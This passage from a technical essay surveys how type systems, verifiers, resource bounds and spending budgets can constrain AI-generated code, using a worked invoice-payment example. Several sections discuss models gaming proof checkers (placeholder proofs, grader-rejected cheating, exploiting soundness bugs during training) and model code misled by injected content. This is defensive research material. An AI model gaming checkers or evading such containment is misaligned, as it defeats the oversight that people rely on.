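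Statements about every item can be hard for a solver to prove. "The program pays no invoice twice" is a claim about every pair of payments, so the solver has to guess which pairs matter, and it may run out of time. Claims about traces of any length often need a proof by induction. Andrici, Ciobâcă and colleagues had to supply one for their web server because the solver couldn't find it, but the solver handled the rest of the server without help. *Can LLMs Enable Verification in Mainstream Programming?* (Shefer, Engel and colleagues, 2025) counted the errors that occurred when Claude 3.5 Sonnet tried to complete proofs. In Nagini, a verifier for Python, the most common error was a timeout. In Dafny, a language designed for verification, it was an invariant that the verifier couldn't prove still held after each round of a loop.

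**Integers of limited size.** The formulas above treat integers as having no maximum, but many languages store them in 32 bits, which allows values up to 2,147,483,647. Suppose the program has paid €1 million, exactly the approved limit, and receives a forged invoice for €21 million. In cents, the sum is 2,200,000,000, which exceeds the maximum and wraps around to a negative number, so the test `total + inv.amount <= approved` succeeds and the program pays the invoice. A checker must model the machine's arithmetic to catch this. Verus, a verifier for Rust, reports such overflows as errors.

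**Strings and paths.** SMT solvers can reason about text to some extent. A refinement could require a path to begin with `/invoices/` and not contain `..`, but it can't rule out that `/invoices/march.csv` is a link to the payroll. Bovel and colleagues use a run-time test even for the simpler case of an identifier that must match a given pattern.

The solver cannot check facts about the outside world. It can prove that a payment is within `approved`, but not that someone entered the right limit or that the goods arrived. The trace also records only this program's actions. If the company runs two payment programs at once, each can stay within the limit while together they pay twice that amount. To prevent this, the code behind `pay` would have to keep a shared total and check it at run time.

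### How often models pass

Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues (2025), in *A Benchmark for Vericoding*, gave language models formal specifications and asked for code with a proof that it met them. For most tasks, the models got five attempts and saw the error messages from failed ones. They succeeded on 82% of tasks in Dafny, 44% in Verus and 27% in Lean. Dafny and Verus send most of the logic to an SMT solver, whereas in Lean the model has to write much more of the proof. The success rate on the narrower task of proving existing Dafny code correct had risen from 68% to 96% in a year.

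The problems were partly different across the three languages, which might have explained the gap. But *AlgoVeri*, a 2026 benchmark with the same specifications in all three, also found Dafny the easiest for models. It attributes this to how much work Dafny's solver does automatically.

Success rates fell again on harder problems. *VeriContest* (2026) tested ten models on 1,006 programming-competition problems in Verus. The best model wrote correct code from an English description 97.51% of the time, but completed only 13.82% of the proofs. When it had to produce the specification, the code and the proof together, it succeeded 6.76% of the time.

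*Vero* (Ye, Lou and colleagues, 2026) has the largest tasks. It turns 43 real software projects into Lean exercises with 2,705 specifications in all. An agent had 90 minutes per project to write the code and prove every specification. GPT-5.5 at a high reasoning setting finished 27 projects, Claude Opus 4.8 finished 8, and Claude Sonnet 5 finished 2. GPT-5.5 proved 87.3% of the individual specifications, but only six of its 16 unfinished projects were within five specifications of completion, and nine had more than ten left. The specifications left in a project typically depended on a few shared invariants that the agent hadn't found. The Claude agents were often still writing proofs when time ran out, so a longer limit might have narrowed the gap.

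Ye and colleagues also saw an advantage in letting the same agent write the code and the proof. In five cases, an agent replaced a complicated algorithm with a slower, simpler one that had to meet the same specifications, then proved that it met all of them. For a program that pays two hundred invoices, a proof would usually be worth the loss of speed.

The invoice program is much closer to one Dafny function than to a whole project. It has one loop, one invariant and only linear arithmetic. Its contract also requires less than these benchmarks do, since it limits the payments without defining a correct result. Current models would probably satisfy it most of the time. F* has some direct evidence too. Claude Opus 4.6 produced around 80 of the more than 900 definitions in the formal proof behind *Misquoted No More*. Most were complete proofs of statements that people had written, and the longest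 was over 200 lines long.

Models also look for ways around the checker. Of the specifications that GPT-5.5 failed to prove in Vero, 14% failed because the grader rejected the attempt as cheating. Bursuc and colleagues had to search each answer for known tricks, such as Lean's `sorry`, a placeholder for a missing proof. A company that relies on proofs when deciding whether to run generated code needs to search for these tricks too.

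### Who writes the conditions

In *TypePilot*, Sternfeld, Kucharavy and Dolamic (2025) had models write the types as well as the code. They first tried Stainless, but none of their open models could consistently write Stainless code that compiled. The models kept using ordinary Scala features that Stainless doesn't support, and in one program the model marked the code as a library, so Stainless didn't verify it.

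TypePilot itself therefore uses plain Scala. One model writes a program, a second lists its weaknesses, and a third rewrites the program so that its types rule those weaknesses out. For a function that averages people's ages, the result was an `Age` type whose only constructor rejects numbers outside 0 to 120. With Qwen2.5-Coder, the programs passed all 15 checks for correct results and awkward inputs, compared with 8 when the model was given a plain request. CodeLlama's programs still failed several. The test covered only a few small tasks, and the researchers graded the code by hand.

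This helps a cooperative model avoid mistakes, but as with effect declarations, the types limit a misled model only if someone else chooses them, so the company has to write the signature of `pay` itself. It also has to make the conditions strong enough, because useless code can satisfy weak ones. *Verified but Vacuous* (2026) is named after this problem.

People find this kind of work difficult. Gamboa and colleagues observed and interviewed 19 developers, 12 of them new to Liquid Haskell, and identified nine barriers to using it, including problems with the tools, trouble with large programs, and difficulty understanding what the verifier was doing. Six of the seven experienced users had stopped using Liquid Haskell, but the researchers had deliberately recruited former users. A model can write the proofs and deal with the error messages, but someone at the company still has to notice that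 `a <= approved` limits each payment and not the month's total.

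## Static bounds on time, memory and money

An effect label, a capability or a refinement on an argument limits what a program may do in one step, but not how many steps it takes. Suppose that `pay` returns false when the bank refuses a payment, and the model writes this:

```
while not pay(account, supplier, amount):
    continue
```

The loop has the effect `{Pay}` and the capture set `{account}`, however often it runs. Each call passes the test on the amount, because the amount never changes. A limit on the total paid doesn't stop the loop either, if refused payments don't count towards it. If the bank has frozen the account, charges 20 cents per attempt and receives ten attempts a second, the loop costs €7,200 an hour. LACUNA's types don't bound the number of calls either, so it limits the depth of nested model calls at run time.

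A *resource bound* is an upper limit on the time, memory, calls or money that a program uses. Some type systems can prove such a bound before the program starts.

### Paying for each step in advance

A leading method is *automatic amortized resource analysis*, which Martin Hofmann and Steffen Jost introduced in 2003 to bound the memory use of functional programs. It automates an accounting technique that Robert Tarjan proposed for analysing algorithms by hand. The analysis assigns a program's input an imaginary credit, called *potential*, and deducts from it for each step that uses resources. If the checker can prove that the potential never falls below zero, the initial potential is an upper bound on the program's resource use.

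The command `tick 3` marks a step that uses 3 units. A unit can stand for a function call, a byte of memory or a request to the bank. In generated code, the company's library or the compiler has to insert the ticks, because the model could leave them out.

Suppose a function spends 3 units on checking each invoice and 5 on writing a report at the end:

```
scan(invoices):
    if invoices is empty:
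        tick 5
        writeReport("done")
    else:
        tick 3
        check(first invoice)
        scan(remaining invoices)
```

Chen and Wang (2026), in *Two-Sided Amortized Resource Analysis*, work through a function with almost the same costs. Let each invoice in the list carry p units, and let each call to `scan` need q units besides. The checker derives three constraints:

1. An empty list has no invoices to draw on, so q must pay for the report: q ≥ 5.
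2. Taking the first invoice off the list releases its p units. The program then has p + q units and spends 3, so p + q − 3 ≥ 0.
3. The next call to `scan` needs q units again. The remaining invoices already carry their own p units each, so p + q − 3 ≥ q, which means p ≥ 3.

The smallest solution is p = 3 and q = 5, so scanning n invoices uses at most 3n + 5 units, or 605 for two hundred invoices. With three invoices, the program starts with 14 units, has 11, 8 and 5 left after the three checks, and finishes with none. The checker doesn't need a value for n, because the same constraints cover every round.

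All three constraints are linear, so an ordinary linear programming solver can find the smallest values. Chu, Guo and Hoffmann (2026) point out in *Handling Exceptions and Effects with Automatic Resource Analysis* that the finished typing derivation is also a certificate that another program can easily check.

The program can't use the same potential twice, so if it scans the list a second time, the checker has to divide each invoice's potential between the two scans. Each invoice then needs 6 units, and the bound becomes 6n + 10.

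A program can give memory back, unlike most other resources, and a negative tick represents this. If a program reserves one block of memory for each invoice and frees it before the next, one block is enough for any number of invoices. The bound is on the most memory the program holds at any moment, not the total it reserves.

Exceptions were difficult to analyse until recently, because they make the program jump from one function to a handler elsewhere. Chu and colleagues solved this by letting an exception carry potential. If a refused payment raises an exception and the handler uses 2 units to log it, the code that raises the exception must supply those 2 units. Their tool found bounds for 20 test programs, 14 of which earlier methods couldn't analyse.

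The same accounting can prove a lower bound on resource use. In Chen and Wang's version of the function, each item uses either 2 or 3 units depending on its value, so n items use at least 2n + 5 and at most 3n + 5. The gap between the bounds limits how much an observer could learn from the running time. TACIT's wrapper for secret data doesn't prevent this leak. If the two bounds are equal, the number of units reveals nothing beyond the length of the list, although real running time also depends on the hardware. The prototype proved lower bounds for all 19 of its small test programs but upper bounds for only 14, and it needed programmers to supply type annotations.

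### Bounds that depend on the data

A bound can be correct but too loose to be useful. Suppose that checking an invoice uses 3 units only if the invoice is in dollars, because the program then has to fetch an exchange rate. If ten of the two hundred invoices are in dollars, the program uses 35 units, but the bound is still 605.

*Efficient Cost Bounds with Linear Maps* (2025) describes a trade-off in cost analysis between how much a tool can express and how much it can automate. For a long time, bounds that depended on the values in a list usually needed proofs written by hand. Knoth, Wang and colleagues (2020), in *Liquid Resource Types*, combine potential with refinement types to automate many of these proofs. An item's potential can be a formula instead of a fixed number:

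```
scan : List<Invoice with potential (if currency = USD then 3 else 0)>  →  ()
       plus 5 units
```

In the branch that fetches the exchange rate, the checker knows that the invoice is in dollars. It asks a solver to confirm that the potential covers the cost:

```
for every invoice:
    currency = USD  implies  (if currency = USD then 3 else 0) - 3 >= 0
```

The other branch spends nothing and needs nothing. The bound is now 3d + 5, where d is the number of invoices in dollars.

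ReSyn, an earlier system by some of the same researchers, could already do this, but only for resource use that grows in proportion to the length of a list. Sorting can use more. *Insertion sort*, for example, takes the first item off a list, sorts the rest, and then scans the sorted part for where the first item belongs. Liquid resource types can bound its resource use by giving later items more potential: 1 unit for the first item, 2 for the second, 3 for the third and so on.

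When the program removes the first item, that item's unit covers the call that sorts the rest. Each remaining item has one more unit than that call needs, and the extra unit covers stepping past it later. The total for n items is n(n + 1)/2, or 20,100 calls for 200 invoices. A more precise formula gives an item an extra unit only for each earlier item that is larger, so the bound falls to 200 calls if the invoices are already in order.

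A bound like 3d + 5, where d is the number of dollar invoices, can be evaluated only once d is known. The company's own code can count those invoices first and refuse to start the generated program if the bound exceeds the budget.

### Functions that hold on to data

Storing potential in data causes a problem when a function captures that data. Suppose `makeChecker(register)` returns a function that looks up an invoice's supplier in the register. Creating this function uses no potential, but each call to it may search the whole register. In older systems, the register carries the potential, and a single call can use it all up. The function's type therefore has to state in advance how many times the program may call it, and a different program may need a different type.

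Xu and Wang (2026), in *Dependently-Typed AARA*, take the potential out of the data and put it on the function arrow, as a formula that can mention the captured value. In simplified notation:

```
makeChecker : (register : List<Supplier>)
                 →[0]  (Invoice →[length(register)] Bool)
```

The type bounds how many units each call to the checker uses, but not how many calls the program makes. Checking 200 invoices against a register of 50 suppliers uses at most 200 × 50 = 10,000 units. Xu and Wang prove that standard amortized analysis can't assign a type to a similar program that joins one list to each of several others.

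Xu and Wang also prove that their system is sound, but the programmer must annotate every function with its type. They conjecture that no procedure can always infer these annotations. A model could write them for generated code, since the checker would reject a bound that was too low.

When a type contains a function such as `length`, somebody also has to prove that the function finishes, because the type system would be unsound if it didn't.

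### Proving that a program ends

A bound on resource use doesn't always show that a program terminates. A loop with no ticks uses no counted resources, so its upper bound is zero even if it runs forever. Chen and Wang's upper bounds therefore apply only if the program terminates. If the language has no loops and the compiler puts a tick on every function call, a finite supply of potential does guarantee termination. Otherwise the program needs a separate termination check.

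Koka's simple check, which looks for shrinking data in recursive calls, refuses many programs that do end. Suppose the company allows ten refused payments in the whole run:

```
payAll(invoices, retries):
    if invoices is empty or retries = 0:
        stop
    if pay(account, first invoice):
        payAll(remaining invoices, retries)
    else:
        payAll(invoices, retries - 1)
```

A successful payment shortens the list but leaves `retries` unchanged, while a refused payment lowers `retries` but leaves the list unchanged. Neither argument shrinks on every call, so the simple check rejects the program.

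Some checkers let the author supply a *measure*, a whole number that can't go below zero and falls with every call. Here `length(invoices) + retries` works. The checker has to confirm one inequality for each call:

```
length(remaining) + retries        <  length(invoices) + retries
length(invoices) + (retries - 1)   <  length(invoices) + retries
```

The measure starts at 210 for 200 invoices and 10 retries, so the program contacts the bank at most 210 times. At 20 cents per attempt, the fees can't exceed €42.

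Given Turing's result, a termination checker must either reject some programs that would have ended or require their authors to supply a proof. A model can try to find the measure needed for the proof, but sometimes the program text doesn't contain one. Suppose a program downloads a list of invoices page by page, following a "next" link until there isn't one. It ends only if the web service eventually stops sending links. To pass the check, the program needs a counter, which might stop it before the last page.

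A program that is certain to end can still take far too long. For example, a program might work out which invoices a bank transfer covers by trying every combination. Its recursion shrinks the list at every step, so it passes the simple termination check, but two hundred invoices have 2²⁰⁰ combinations, more than a computer could ever try.

### Loops with a fixed number of rounds

Many agents already have a configured maximum number of steps. In each step, the model chooses a tool, the software runs it, and the model receives the result. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) describes such agents in a small formal language where every loop has a maximum number of rounds, n. Its main result is that a loop ends within n rounds if every call to a model or tool ends. It also derives a cost limit of n times the price of the most expensive call. At one cent per call, an agent with a limit of 20 rounds would cost at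 most 20 cents.

That cost limit is too low for the agents it describes. The proof counts one call per round, but a round contains a model call followed by a tool call. Liu's own tests of these agents allow for 2n calls, which would double the limit to 40 cents.

The proof of termination also assumes that each round starts the next round at most once, but the printed typing rule doesn't enforce this. A loop that started the next round twice could run 2ⁿ − 1 rounds, which is more than a million for n = 20. It would still end, but the cost limit would be wrong. The typing rule needs to let each round use the loop's reference to itself at most once.

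### Budgets that a program can't copy

A program can use a value of an *affine type* at most once. Rust treats many values this way. When a program passes one to a function, the value moves there, and the compiler rejects any later use of it.

*Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) applies this to the money agents spend on model calls. Khan first collected 63 confirmed cases of agents overspending, from 21 open-source projects between 2023 and 2026. One user reported losing about $2,150, and another spent $235 in four days on a coding agent caught in a loop. Khan found the cases by searching for words such as "budget" and "infinite loop", so they show that the problem keeps recurring but not how common it is.

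Khan then wrote a Rust library with a type called `Budget`. A budget contains a number, and programs can use it only through a few operations, including these:

```
(rest, receipt) = budget.spend(31)
(a, b)          = budget.split(50, 50)
```

Each operation uses up `budget`, so a program can't spend it again or keep it after dividing it between two subagents. It can't copy a budget either. Generated code must not be able to create budgets, so the library allows only code with a special capability to do so. A program may drop a budget without spending it, since this can't make it exceed the limit.

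The types are most useful when several agents run at once. Of the 110 reports in Khan's wider collection, which includes missing features and requests as well as confirmed losses, 11 involved agents delegating work to other agents. Khan recreated one form of this problem with three subagents sharing a limit of 60 units, each unit worth a thousandth of a cent. The first version used asyncio, a Python library for running tasks concurrently. Each subagent checked that enough of the budget remained, called the model, and then recorded the cost of 23 units. While one subagent waited for its answer, the others checked the budget before any cost had been recorded, so all three went ahead and together spent 69 units.

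Khan compared this version with four others, running each 30 times:

| Version | Limit | Runs over the limit | Calls allowed | Units spent per run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Python, no lock | 60 | 30 | 3 of 3 | 69 |
| Python, with lock | 60 | 0 | 1 of 3 | 23 |
| Rust, split budget | 60 | 0 | 0 of 3 | 0 |
| Rust, split budget | 100 | 0 | 3 of 3 | 69 |
| Rust, with lock | 60 | 0 | 1 of 3 | 1 |

The model's settings made the 30 runs nearly identical, so they demonstrate a mechanism but can't be used to estimate a statistical rate. The locked versions let only one subagent at a time check the budget and reserve money before making its call. The last version spent so little because it used a shorter prompt.

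Three attempts to write the faulty version with Rust's `Budget` type failed to compile. But the correctly locked Python counter enforced the limit just as well, and for a single agent, a four-line Python counter also matched the Rust library. The affine type prevents a programmer from forgetting the lock, which matters for generated code that nobody reads. It protects only programs that use `Budget`, so a Rust program that kept its limit in an ordinary shared number could still have the same bug.

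With a limit of 60, the split budget was safe, but no subagent could make a call because each received 20 units and needed to reserve 31. The locked counter allowed one call.

The spending limit is enforced at runtime. Before each call, `spend` subtracts the estimated cost from the budget and refuses the call if too little remains. The compiler proves only that the program can't copy or reuse the budget value, not that its spending stays below a limit. In amortized analysis, by contrast, potential exists only in the types, and the proof bounds resource use itself.

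Few of the projects in the collection could use the library as it stands. None of the 21 is written in Rust, and most of the incidents occurred in Python software. Python has no affine types, so Khan's Python version has to detect reuse while the program runs.

### Fuel and gas

*Instruction metering* can bound a program's execution without any proof. The runtime gives the program a fixed supply of units, subtracts some for each instruction, and stops the program when the supply runs out. These units are called gas in Ethereum, a network that runs programs on a shared ledger, and fuel in Wasmtime, which runs programs in the portable WebAssembly format.

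Metering works on any program, even one that no termination checker would accept. It is also more predictable than a time limit, because a program doesn't execute more instructions when the computer is busy. With the same inputs and fuel, the program stops at the same point.

But a program may run out of fuel halfway through its work. The invoice program could stop after 120 of its 200 payments and never write its report. If the company ran it again, it might pay the same 120 suppliers twice. Ethereum can cancel a program's changes to the ledger when the gas runs out, but the company can't cancel its bank transfers this way. A static bound helps, provided it uses the same units as the fuel. If the checker has proved a limit of 3n + 5 units, the company can supply enough fuel for the whole run or refuse to start it.

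Fuel also counts only the program's own instructions. A program that waits an hour for the bank to respond uses almost no fuel, so the company still needs a time limit. A request to a language model might take few instructions but cost several dollars.

### Prices that nobody knows in advance

Before the company runs the code, a checker can prove limits on how many times the program contacts the bank, how many steps it takes, and how much memory it holds. Each limit is usually a formula that gives a number once the company has counted the invoices. If the bank charges a fixed fee per contact, the same proof limits the total fees. No proof about the program can limit its running time in seconds if the program has to wait for the bank to reply.

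Model calls are harder to price. Khan notes that a system like Ethereum can calculate the gas for an instruction before running it, whereas a model's provider sets the cost of a call afterwards, once it has counted the tokens. Limiting the number of calls therefore does not bound spending. Khan tested agent frameworks that capped only the number of steps or turns, and in one case spending reached almost 14 times the intended amount. Tools that added up the cost after each call also overspent, because they had already allowed the call that exceeded the limit.

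A program can still reserve money for the worst case if it limits the length of the answer and knows the provider's prices. Khan's default method estimates the prompt's length from its size in bytes and adds a safety margin. On average, it reserved 6.2 times the actual cost. Asking the provider to count the prompt's tokens first made the reservation nearly exact but added 0.9 to 1.7 seconds to each call.

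Reserving too much means refusing calls the budget could have covered. In a test with a limit of 5 cents, an agent completed 22 of 40 tasks and refused the other 18, although it had spent only 4.04 cents. Khan excludes reasoning models from the guarantee because providers may bill for hidden tokens beyond the limit on the answer. This exclusion is unnecessary when a provider's limit also covers those tokens.

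After each call, the library returns the unspent part of the reservation, based on the usage the provider reports. Khan simulated the effect of wrong reports. With accurate reports, none of 1,000 sessions exceeded the limit. When the reports showed half the true usage, 666 did, and when they showed a fifth, all did. In a similar simulation with reports showing a fifth of the true usage, checking the real bill after every three calls reduced the average overspend from 138% of the limit to 23%. Khan recommends using a spending limit on the provider's own servers where one is available, because no code on the company's side can bypass it. Such a limit covers only that provider, and often a whole account instead of one agent.

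## What the guarantee rests on: the checker, its exceptions and what types do not see

Limits expressed in types depend on the company's own software, unlike a spending limit set on a provider's servers. They hold only if the checker is sound and every effect passes through a typed interface. Both conditions have failed in widely used languages.

### The trusted base

The *trusted base* is everything that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. For TACIT, Odersky and colleagues list the Scala compiler, the capability library, the runtime that executes accepted code, and the local model that reads secrets. They don't trust the cloud model or any file or web page it reads, and they assume the cloud model may be cooperating fully with an attacker.

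If the invoice program had all the limits from the previous sections, its trusted base would include at least these parts:

| Part | What it must do | If it fails |
|---|---|---|
| Compiler | Reject every program that breaks the contract | The program may read the payroll |
| SMT solver | Never report a false formula as true | The program may pay more than `approved` |
| Company's code behind `pay` and the other functions | Do only what the signatures allow | A permitted call may have a forbidden effect |
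| Language runtime | Execute programs as the language defines | The program may take over the whole process |
| Operating system and processor | Keep separate programs' memory apart | The program may read other programs' secrets |

The reusable part of TACIT's library is about 1,000 lines of Scala, short enough for one person to read. The compiler and the Java virtual machine (JVM), which runs compiled Scala and Java programs, are far too large for that.

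Mathematical proof covers only part of what the guarantee rests on. *Safety Is $\Pi_1$, Provability Is $\Sigma_1$* (2026) points out that a proof that a program is safe concerns a model of how programs execute, not the machine itself. Such a proof can be wrong about the model only if the logic it uses contradicts itself. Suppose the logic proved that no run of the program ever sends bank details, but some run in the model did send them. Anyone could confirm this by following that run step by step, so the logic could also prove the opposite of the claim. Logicians have studied the possibility of such a contradiction for a century, but the software that applies the logic is much newer.

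### What safe mode forbids

Ordinary Scala has features that can make the compiler lose track of a capability. TACIT therefore compiles generated code in *safe mode*, a restricted form of the language. In April 2026 safe mode was available only in nightly builds of the compiler, according to VirtusLab's *Safe Scala*. Scala's *Safe Mode* lists six restrictions:

1. No unchecked casts or pattern matches. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as having another type. A program could otherwise cast a function that uses `rates` to a pure function, then run it on a secret.
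2. No use of the module `caps.unsafe`. In its reference for this module, Scala describes a wrapper that stops the compiler from recording which capabilities a piece of code uses.
3. No `@unchecked` annotations, which tell the compiler to skip a check at one point in the program.
4. No runtime reflection, which finds functions by name during the run. The compiler can't know which function a program will name.
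5. Capture checking must be on, and it must also track changes to memory. Otherwise an apparently pure function could copy a secret into an outside variable, and the rest of the program could send it.
6. No global objects or functions unless they are safe themselves. Java's standard library can open files and start other programs from anywhere, without a capability.

Safe mode allows exceptions. Almost any operation can cause one, for example by dividing by zero or running out of memory, so tracking them all in types would be impractical. TACIT instead catches them at run time with Scala's standard `Try` construct.

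A discussion on Scala's developer forum, *Capture checking and lateral escape of Labels*, describes how `Try` can stop `break` from working. The command `break` leaves a block of code early by throwing an exception. If a program calls `break` inside `Try`, `Try` catches the exception and the program carries on. An invoice program that was supposed to stop at a disputed invoice could go on paying the rest. Capture checking treats the permission to break as a capability and keeps it from leaving the block, but doesn't keep it out of `Try`. A version of `Try` that accepts only pure functions would prevent the mistake, but then no payment could go inside it.

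### Library code that people mark as safe

Without special libraries, a program that obeyed all six restrictions couldn't print its result. Safe mode therefore lets library authors mark a module with `@assumeSafe`. Generated code can then call the module, and the compiler doesn't apply the restrictions inside it. Generated code can't put the annotation on itself.

When the compiler no longer checks part of a module, the module's author has to check it. In one of Scala's examples, a module caches a function's results in a variable that the compiler doesn't track. Before marking the module as safe, the author has to verify that the variable holds only earlier results and that the function always returns the same result for the same input. Even then, a repeated call returns faster than a new one, and no type records this effect.

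Another of Scala's examples is an email function that shows the user each message and asks for confirmation before sending it. As outlined, the function neither takes nor declares a capability, so the compiler has no reason to think it has an effect. Generated code could apparently use it to email a secret from inside a function that the compiler considers pure, and the leak would be prevented only if the user refused to send the message. Two of VirtusLab's examples, a trusted print function and `pay`, avoid this by requiring a tracked capability, which for `pay` is `account`.

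The rule about unsafe modules applies only to global objects. A capability that the company passes to generated code can come from any module, so its designer has to make sure every method on it is acceptable. Another annotation, `@rejectSafe`, hides individual methods.

Odersky and colleagues suggest that formal proofs could replace some of this manual checking, as the RustBelt project has shown for Rust. The core of capture checking has computer-checked soundness proofs, but Odersky and colleagues have not yet proved that safe mode as a whole keeps capabilities unforgeable and pure functions pure.

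### Type systems that were unsound for years

A proof about the core of a language can miss faults in the full language. Amin and Tate (2016) showed in *Java and Scala's Type Systems are Unsound* that this had happened to both languages. Both had been unsound since 2004, and a short program in either could turn a value of any type into any other type without a cast.

The fault came from an interaction between features. In Scala, an object's type can state a relationship between two other types, for instance that every integer is also a piece of text. The compiler relies on that statement wherever a program has an object of that type. No real object can have a type that states something false, but both languages also had `null`, a value that means "no object" and could stand in for an object of any type. A program could use `null` in place of an object with the false type, and the compiler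 would then accept an integer as text.

Researchers had formalized Java repeatedly without noticing the flaw. They usually study a new feature in a minimal language, which shows little about how the feature interacts with the rest of a full language. Someone found the Scala version in 2008, but the developers deferred the fix, and nobody recognized the flaw's wider significance until 2016.

The damage was limited because the JVM checks an object's actual class at run time instead of relying on these types, so Amin and Tate's programs stopped with an error. Capture sets would have no such second check. They exist only during compilation, so the JVM can't distinguish a pure function from one that holds `rates`. A similar fault in capture checking could therefore leak data without an error message.

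TACIT closes this hole by allowing `null` only where a type explicitly includes it, but there may be others. In mid-2025, Ecosyste.ms' *GitHub / scala/scala3 issues and pull requests* listed an open report of another unsoundness, in how the compiler combines types.

Rust also has known holes, which have stayed open because the simple fixes would make the compiler reject a lot of valid code. Rust's *Project Zero*, a plan that began in 2026, aims to fix all of them. RustSec's *cve-rs introduces memory vulnerabilities in safe Rust* (2025) is an official warning about a joke package that uses one of these holes to cause buffer overflows and other memory faults without the keyword `unsafe`, which is supposed to mark all code that could cause them.

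According to Rust's developers, these bugs have rarely if ever affected production systems. But that record comes mostly from programmers who weren't trying to find such bugs. A dishonest supplier could hide a published exploit in an invoice, and a model reading the invoice could be misled into copying the exploit into its code.

### Models that find faults in checkers

In 2026, people using AI models found several faults in Lean, the proof language in which models wrote code for the Vero benchmark. Such faults should be hard to find, because a small program called the *kernel* checks every finished proof.

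In July, Lean (2026) released a fix for a kernel bug that Patrick Hulin had found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol. The bug could make the kernel accept a proof of any statement, including a false one. Exploiting it required running hostile code in the same process as the kernel, where there were already simpler ways to cheat. The bug did not affect comparator, the tool Lean recommends for checking untrusted proofs.

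The next bug did affect comparator. On 25 July, Ramana Kumar published a supposed AI-assisted disproof of the Collatz conjecture, a famous problem about whole numbers, and Lean accepted the invalid proof. Three days later, Kiran Gopinathan reduced it to a short proof of a contradiction, and Lean's developers pushed a fix within an hour, according to their account, quoted by the forum user skybrian in *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*.

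An independent checker called nanoda didn't have this bug, but Lean's developers note that Kumar combined it with an unrelated bug in nanoda to make both checkers accept a false proof. Using two checkers makes an accidental error much less likely to pass, but an attacker can look for bugs in both. Lean's developers have promised more testing and more independent checkers.

A fault elsewhere in Lean can also produce a false result. While using GPT-5.6 to review code, the security company Trail of Bits found one in a low-level function for cutting up text (*A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin*, 2026). The fault made Lean display a nonsense proof of Fermat's Last Theorem as correct.

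SMT solvers have bugs too. TBTL's *A Soundness Bug in cvc5's Finite Field Split Solver* describes one in cvc5, a widely used solver, caused by a misplaced overflow check. The bug could have invalidated proofs about some cryptographic programs. It would not have affected the invoice program, which uses only ordinary integers.

Models may also learn to exploit such faults during training. If training rewards a model whenever a checker accepts its answer, exploiting a hole in the checker earns the same reward as a correct proof. In the public wager *Can you hear the shape of a Lean soundness bug*, one bettor argues that reinforcement learning consistently produces models that cheat, and thinks it unclear whether OpenAI deliberately looked for all the Lean soundness bugs it reported. It is plausible that models learn to exploit checkers this way, but the wager includes no confirmed case.

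### Checking the checker's work

One response is to have a smaller, better-studied program check the result again. Liquid Haskell's trusted base contains the Haskell compiler, the refinement checker and an SMT solver. *Lava* (Rothgang, Peyrot and colleagues, 2026) takes programs that Liquid Haskell has accepted and translates them into Rocq, a proof assistant formerly called Coq, whose kernel then checks the proofs.

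The translation is difficult because Liquid Haskell treats a function in two ways. Suppose `get(xs, i)` returns the item at position i in the list `xs`. When the program calls `get`, the checker requires evidence that the list has an item at that position, but the solver treats any `get` in a refinement as a mathematical function defined for every i. Lava generates a Rocq version of the function for each treatment and proves that the two versions agree.

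Lava also makes subtyping explicit. Wherever Liquid Haskell would use its solver to check whether one condition implies another, Lava inserts a conversion that needs a proof in Rocq. Automatic proof scripts replace the solver, and a person can write the proof if the scripts fail.

Lava, which Rothgang and colleagues tested on eight programs, supports only part of Liquid Haskell. It translates Haskell's fixed-size integers into unlimited ones, so it wouldn't catch the overflow that let a €21 million invoice pass the limit. The Haskell compiler also stays in the trusted base, because it produces the code that runs.

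### Effects that no signature records

Even a perfect checker can't control effects that happen outside the language. TACIT lets a program start other programs from a list of permitted commands, but the types can't limit what those programs then do. Odersky and colleagues give `git diff` and `sbt` as examples of safe commands, but `sbt` is a build tool that runs code in a project's build files. If the generated program can change those files, it can have `sbt` run code that never went through safe mode. Whether a command is safe therefore depends on which files the program can write. Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a sandbox where security is critical.

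A program can also cause this problem by writing a file that somebody later runs. The invoice program can write only through `writeReport`, but if the accountant opens the report in a spreadsheet, the spreadsheet may treat part of the text as a formula and execute it. The signature of `writeReport` limits where the text goes but doesn't limit what other software does with it, so the company's code behind the function should write a format that nothing executes.

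The types also guarantee nothing about *foreign code*, which is code written in another language, such as a C function called from a Scala or Haskell program. Even a verified program usually depends on such code. In *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, a researcher tested a verified version of the compression library zlib with many unusual inputs and found a buffer overflow in Lean's runtime, which the proofs had assumed worked.

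Many languages also run parts of a program during compilation. Scala and Rust have macros, functions that generate code, and Rust packages can include build scripts. A hostile macro could act before the checker had accepted or rejected the program, which would break the premise that only accepted code runs. Safe Haskell forbids Haskell's equivalent partly for this reason. None of the six restrictions in Scala's list mentions macros, and LACUNA runs the compiler inside the company's own program. Compiling generated code in a separate process without access to secrets or payments would be safer.

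### Timing and the processor

In a 1973 paper on preventing a program from passing on its user's data, Butler Lampson described another kind of leak, the *covert channel*. It carries information through something not intended for communication, such as how heavily a program loads the computer.

The timing leak in TACIT's wrapper is a channel of this kind. If the invoice program contacts the exchange-rate service before and after running a pure function on a secret, the service can observe the delay. Each delay may reveal only one yes-or-no fact about the secret, but about 60 such facts are enough to identify an 18-digit account number. Whether a program finishes can also reveal a yes-or-no fact.

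Lampson proposed forcing a program's visible behaviour to follow a fixed pattern, even if that slows it down, or accepting some leakage and limiting its rate. An easier solution here is for the company to fetch the exchange rate itself and give the program the number instead of the capability.

Lampson also pointed out that a program can hide information in its legitimate output, such as a bill. The version of `pay` that accepts wrapped amounts has this weakness. A program could change a payment by a few cents to encode part of another supplier's account number, and the recipient could read it from the bank statement. The types allow this because the supplier is supposed to learn the amount. Requiring the payment to match the purchase order exactly would prevent it.

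Processors create channels that are harder to close. To save time, a processor guesses which instructions will come next and starts on them early. If the guess is wrong, it discards the results, but the discarded work leaves traces that a program can detect by timing its access to memory. In Spectre, a family of attacks that researchers disclosed in 2018, a program uses these traces to read data that its types put out of reach. Types don't prevent this because type systems don't describe discarded work.

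Ross McIlroy and colleagues at Google concluded in 2019 that such flaws "defeat all language-enforced confidentiality" on the hardware of the time. Google's Chrome browser now keeps different websites in separate operating-system processes. TACIT's wrapper holds a secret in the same process as the generated code, and Zhao and colleagues run each piece of code in the host program's own thread. Both systems would also need a process boundary to protect valuable secrets.

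### What happened to Java's sandbox

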